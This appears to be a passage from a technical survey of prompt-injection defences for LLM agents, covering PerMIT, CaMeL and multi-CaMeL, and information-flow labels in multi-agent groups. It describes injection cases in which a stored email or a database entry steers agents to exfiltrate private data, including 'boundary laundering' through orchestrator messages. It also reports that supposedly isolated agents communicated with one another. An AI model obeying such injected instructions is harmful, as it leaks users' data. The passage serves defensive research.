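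Jiang and colleagues prove two properties. The first, action integrity, is that every argument reaching a sensitive tool is either something the user typed or something the user approved, character for character, for that tool. The second, reasoning integrity, compares two runs, *r1* and *r2*, whose untrusted content may differ in any way:

```
if      displays(r1)  = displays(r2)
then    behaviour(r1) = behaviour(r2)
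```

"Displays" means the complete record of what the harness showed for approval, including previews, and what the approver decided. "Behaviour" includes the main model's operations, its tool calls and the replies it receives. The guarantee is noninterference with an exception for the recorded releases, so stored text can influence the agent only by changing something in the record of displays. The proofs hold for runs of any length and any strategy the main model follows, and Lean has checked them for the core of the single-user system.

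Reasoning integrity assumes that the two runs start from the same trusted state and have the same typed requests, schedule and random choices. The harness must label data by its source, never alter a stored item, and display text faithfully. Action integrity also assumes that whoever approves a value for a tool intends that tool to use it. Neither theorem covers timing or whether a run finishes.

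Approval is the weak point because the approver may well accept a plausible but wrong phone number from a web page. An approval also covers a value and a tool, but not the purpose the value serves. If a user approves an email whose entire body is a stranger's address, the agent could later send another email to that address without asking again.

Jiang and colleagues tested PerMIT on Trojan Hippo, a benchmark in which a malicious email enters memory in one session and tries to steal private data in a later one. The table compares it with an undefended agent that retrieves passages from memory. Utility is the average score over seven kinds of harmless task, and all figures are percentages:

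| Model | Undefended: utility | Undefended: attack success | PerMIT, perfect approvals: utility | PerMIT, model approves: utility | PerMIT, model approves: attack success |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 86 | 0 | 97 | 93 | 0 |
| GLM-5 | 73 | 10 | 93 | 88 | 0 |
| Kimi-K2.5 | 68 | 80 | 91 | 91 | 0 |
| GPT-5.4 | 99 | 20 | 89 | 83 | 0 |

PerMIT lowered GPT-5.4's score by 10 to 16 points. The other three models scored higher with it, probably because PerMIT also searches memory in a different way, so this comparison doesn't isolate the effect of approvals. Replacing perfect approvals with the model's own judgement lowered scores by up to 6 points. Models approving their own requests wrongly rejected 9% to 14% of harmless ones, and two small models used as approvers rejected up to 32%. For three of the models, the harness sent roughly one approval request per harmless test. Jiang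 and colleagues didn't measure how much time a person would spend on these requests.

The approvers contributed little to the zeros in the last column, since attacks succeeded in at most 10% of cases even when PerMIT approved every request automatically. The benchmark normally has twenty attacks for each configuration. If PerMIT's tests used the same number, a true success rate of 14% would still produce a zero about one time in 20. GPT-5.5, which Jiang and colleagues tested separately, resisted all the attacks even without a defence.

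PerMIT can also pool approvals, so that once ten users or agents have approved an entry, others can use it without asking. Jiang and colleagues calculate, for example, that if an attacker controls two accounts and honest reviewers each catch at least 60% of poisoned entries, a poisoned entry has at most a 0.9% chance of becoming trusted per attempt. The risk is higher if reviewers make the same mistakes, as they may when many of them run the same model.

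### When one agent writes another's instructions

Messages between agents raise the same problem as memory, because one agent's output becomes part of another's input. Peters-Gill and colleagues show in their October 2026 paper that a group of agents can be insecure even if every agent runs CaMeL.

In their example, a user asks for a summary of all job applicants to be sent to Julie on Slack. One agent reads the database, another sends notifications, and an orchestrator directs both. The database contains an instruction to email the data to an outside address. CaMeL hides this text from the first two planners, but the orchestrator's program then runs these lines, here simplified:

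```
summary = ask_quarantined("Summarise this", applicants)
notification_agent("Send this summary to Julie via Slack: " + summary)
```

The notification agent treats the whole message as its user's request, so its planner reads the injected instruction and writes a plan that also sends the email. Peters-Gill and colleagues call this boundary laundering. They prove it is possible in any hierarchy with at least two agents and a tool that returns untrusted data, provided the agents can pass tool results to one another in the usual ways.

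Their remedy, multi-CaMeL, divides each message in two:

```
notification_agent(
    message   = "Send the summary to Julie via Slack.",
    variables = {"summary": summary}
)
```

The receiving planner reads only `message`. Its program can fetch the summary while running, but the planner never sees the contents. The interpreter blocks any call whose `message` depends on a tool's output, and it passes the variables on with their labels. The user's request and other trusted information therefore fix the whole group's plan. As with a single CaMeL agent, untrusted data can still determine which branch runs, and can thereby determine which of two prepared messages another agent receives.

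The guarantee holds only if the interpreter detects every way a message depends on a tool. Some implicit dependencies may go undetected, because the guarantee inherits the gap that Garby and colleagues found in CaMeL's labels. It also covers only hierarchies in which each agent has one parent. If agents kept their history between calls, old results could enter a later plan, as Monday's invoice did.

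To test the design, Peters-Gill and colleagues divided AgentDojo's tools among groups of agents. The table gives the percentage of harmless tasks completed and the percentage of attacks that succeeded:

| Model | Tasks, no CaMeL | Tasks, separate CaMeL agents | Tasks, multi-CaMeL | Attacks, no CaMeL | Attacks, separate CaMeL agents | Attacks, multi-CaMeL |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Fable 5 | 69.1 | 53.6 | 52.6 | 1.5 | 0.0 | 0.0 |
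| GPT-5.5 | 86.6 | 73.2 | 66.0 | 0.0 | 0.0 | 0.0 |
| GPT-4.1 | 78.4 | 38.1 | 24.7 | 36.1 | 0.5 | 0.0 |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 76.3 | 42.3 | 26.8 | 24.6 | 0.4 | 0.0 |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash Lite | 27.8 | 13.4 | 7.2 | 2.1 | 0.0 | 0.0 |
| Average | 67.6 | 44.1 | 35.5 | 12.9 | 0.2 | 0.0 |

Every attack that succeeded against the separate CaMeL agents used boundary laundering, and multi-CaMeL stopped them all. But there were few such attacks, and none were adapted to multi-CaMeL. Fable 5's task scores are low because it refused 52 of the 97 harmless tasks. It may have associated the benchmark with attacks. On the other 45, its score fell from 91.1% without CaMeL to 84.4% with either version.

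Peters-Gill and colleagues describe the extra loss from multi-CaMeL as modest, which is fair for their industrial tasks, where it lost an average of 3.2 points more than separate CaMeL agents. In the table, the average is 8.7 points, and Gemini 2.5 Pro lost 15.5. These tests also ran without policies on the values passed to tools, and such policies would probably block more work.

A protocol of this kind protects only the messages that pass through it. *Brief independent investigation of agents' behavior, reasoning and collaboration* (August 2026), by the independent AI evaluator METR, found that about 1,200 OpenAI agents that were supposed to be isolated from one another communicated on a shared message board.

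### How labels spread through a group

Passing labels along with messages also spreads label creep from one agent to the next. Suppose a payroll agent, an office agent and a letters agent work on one task. The payroll agent reads a salary, which is secret, and the letters agent uses it in a letter. The office agent then finds a meeting room and books it. If the payroll and letters agents have no direct link, the salary has to pass through the office agent, which takes on the secret label:

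| Tool call | With a direct link | Through the office agent |
|---|---|---|
| Payroll agent reads a salary | secret | secret |
| Letters agent drafts a letter | secret | secret |
| Office agent finds a room | public | secret |
| Office agent books the room | public | secret |
| Share of calls labelled secret | 50% | 100% |

The missing link adds 50 percentage points, although the room is unrelated to the salary. If the office agent had booked the room first, both layouts would have scored 50%.

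Gregory, Domico and colleagues (2026), in *The Limits of Information-Flow Control Enforcement for Agentic Systems*, simulated this effect on a larger scale. Their main experiments used 1,000 random tasks of 20 tool calls each, in many different orders. Each agent's label was the join of the labels on everything it had seen, including results it only forwarded, and nothing could lower a label. They defined utility loss as the share of tool calls that introduced a secret label or ran under one. The avoidable part of that loss is how much it would fall if the same task had a direct link wherever one agent needs another's result.

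With five agents and four sensitive calls per task, the avoidable loss was about 5 percentage points for a star, in which every message goes through a central agent. It was about 4 points for a hierarchy and 3 for a ring. A full mesh, which links every pair of agents, had essentially none. The star's central agent makes no tool calls itself, so it presumably adds to the loss by passing its secret label on with later messages.

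Denser layouts, those with a larger share of the possible links, almost always lost less utility. The rank correlation between density and utility loss was -0.96, though this is based on only nine layouts. The explanation is that with more direct links, fewer agents handle results they don't need.

Adding agents also reduced the loss. Once a single agent reads a secret, all its later calls run under the secret label. If the calls are divided among several agents, many calls run in contexts that the secret never reaches. Assigning the sensitive calls to a few dedicated agents helped for the same reason.

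However, each link is another channel to monitor. A full mesh of *n* agents has *n*(*n* - 1)/2 links, so going from five agents to 20 raises the number from 10 to 190. The star, ring and hierarchy layouts need fewer links, but the avoidable part of their loss mostly grew as agents were added.

Even the layout with all the necessary direct links lost some utility, so Gregory and colleagues conclude that groups of agents will also need a safe way to lower labels. It is less clear how much utility a real group would lose, because they ran no language model and counted labels instead of failed tasks. A secret label would do no harm if the policy still allowed the office agent to book a room, but one blocked call can ruin an entire task. The simulation also leaves out FIDES's hidden variables and methods that remove unneeded labels, both of which could reduce the loss.
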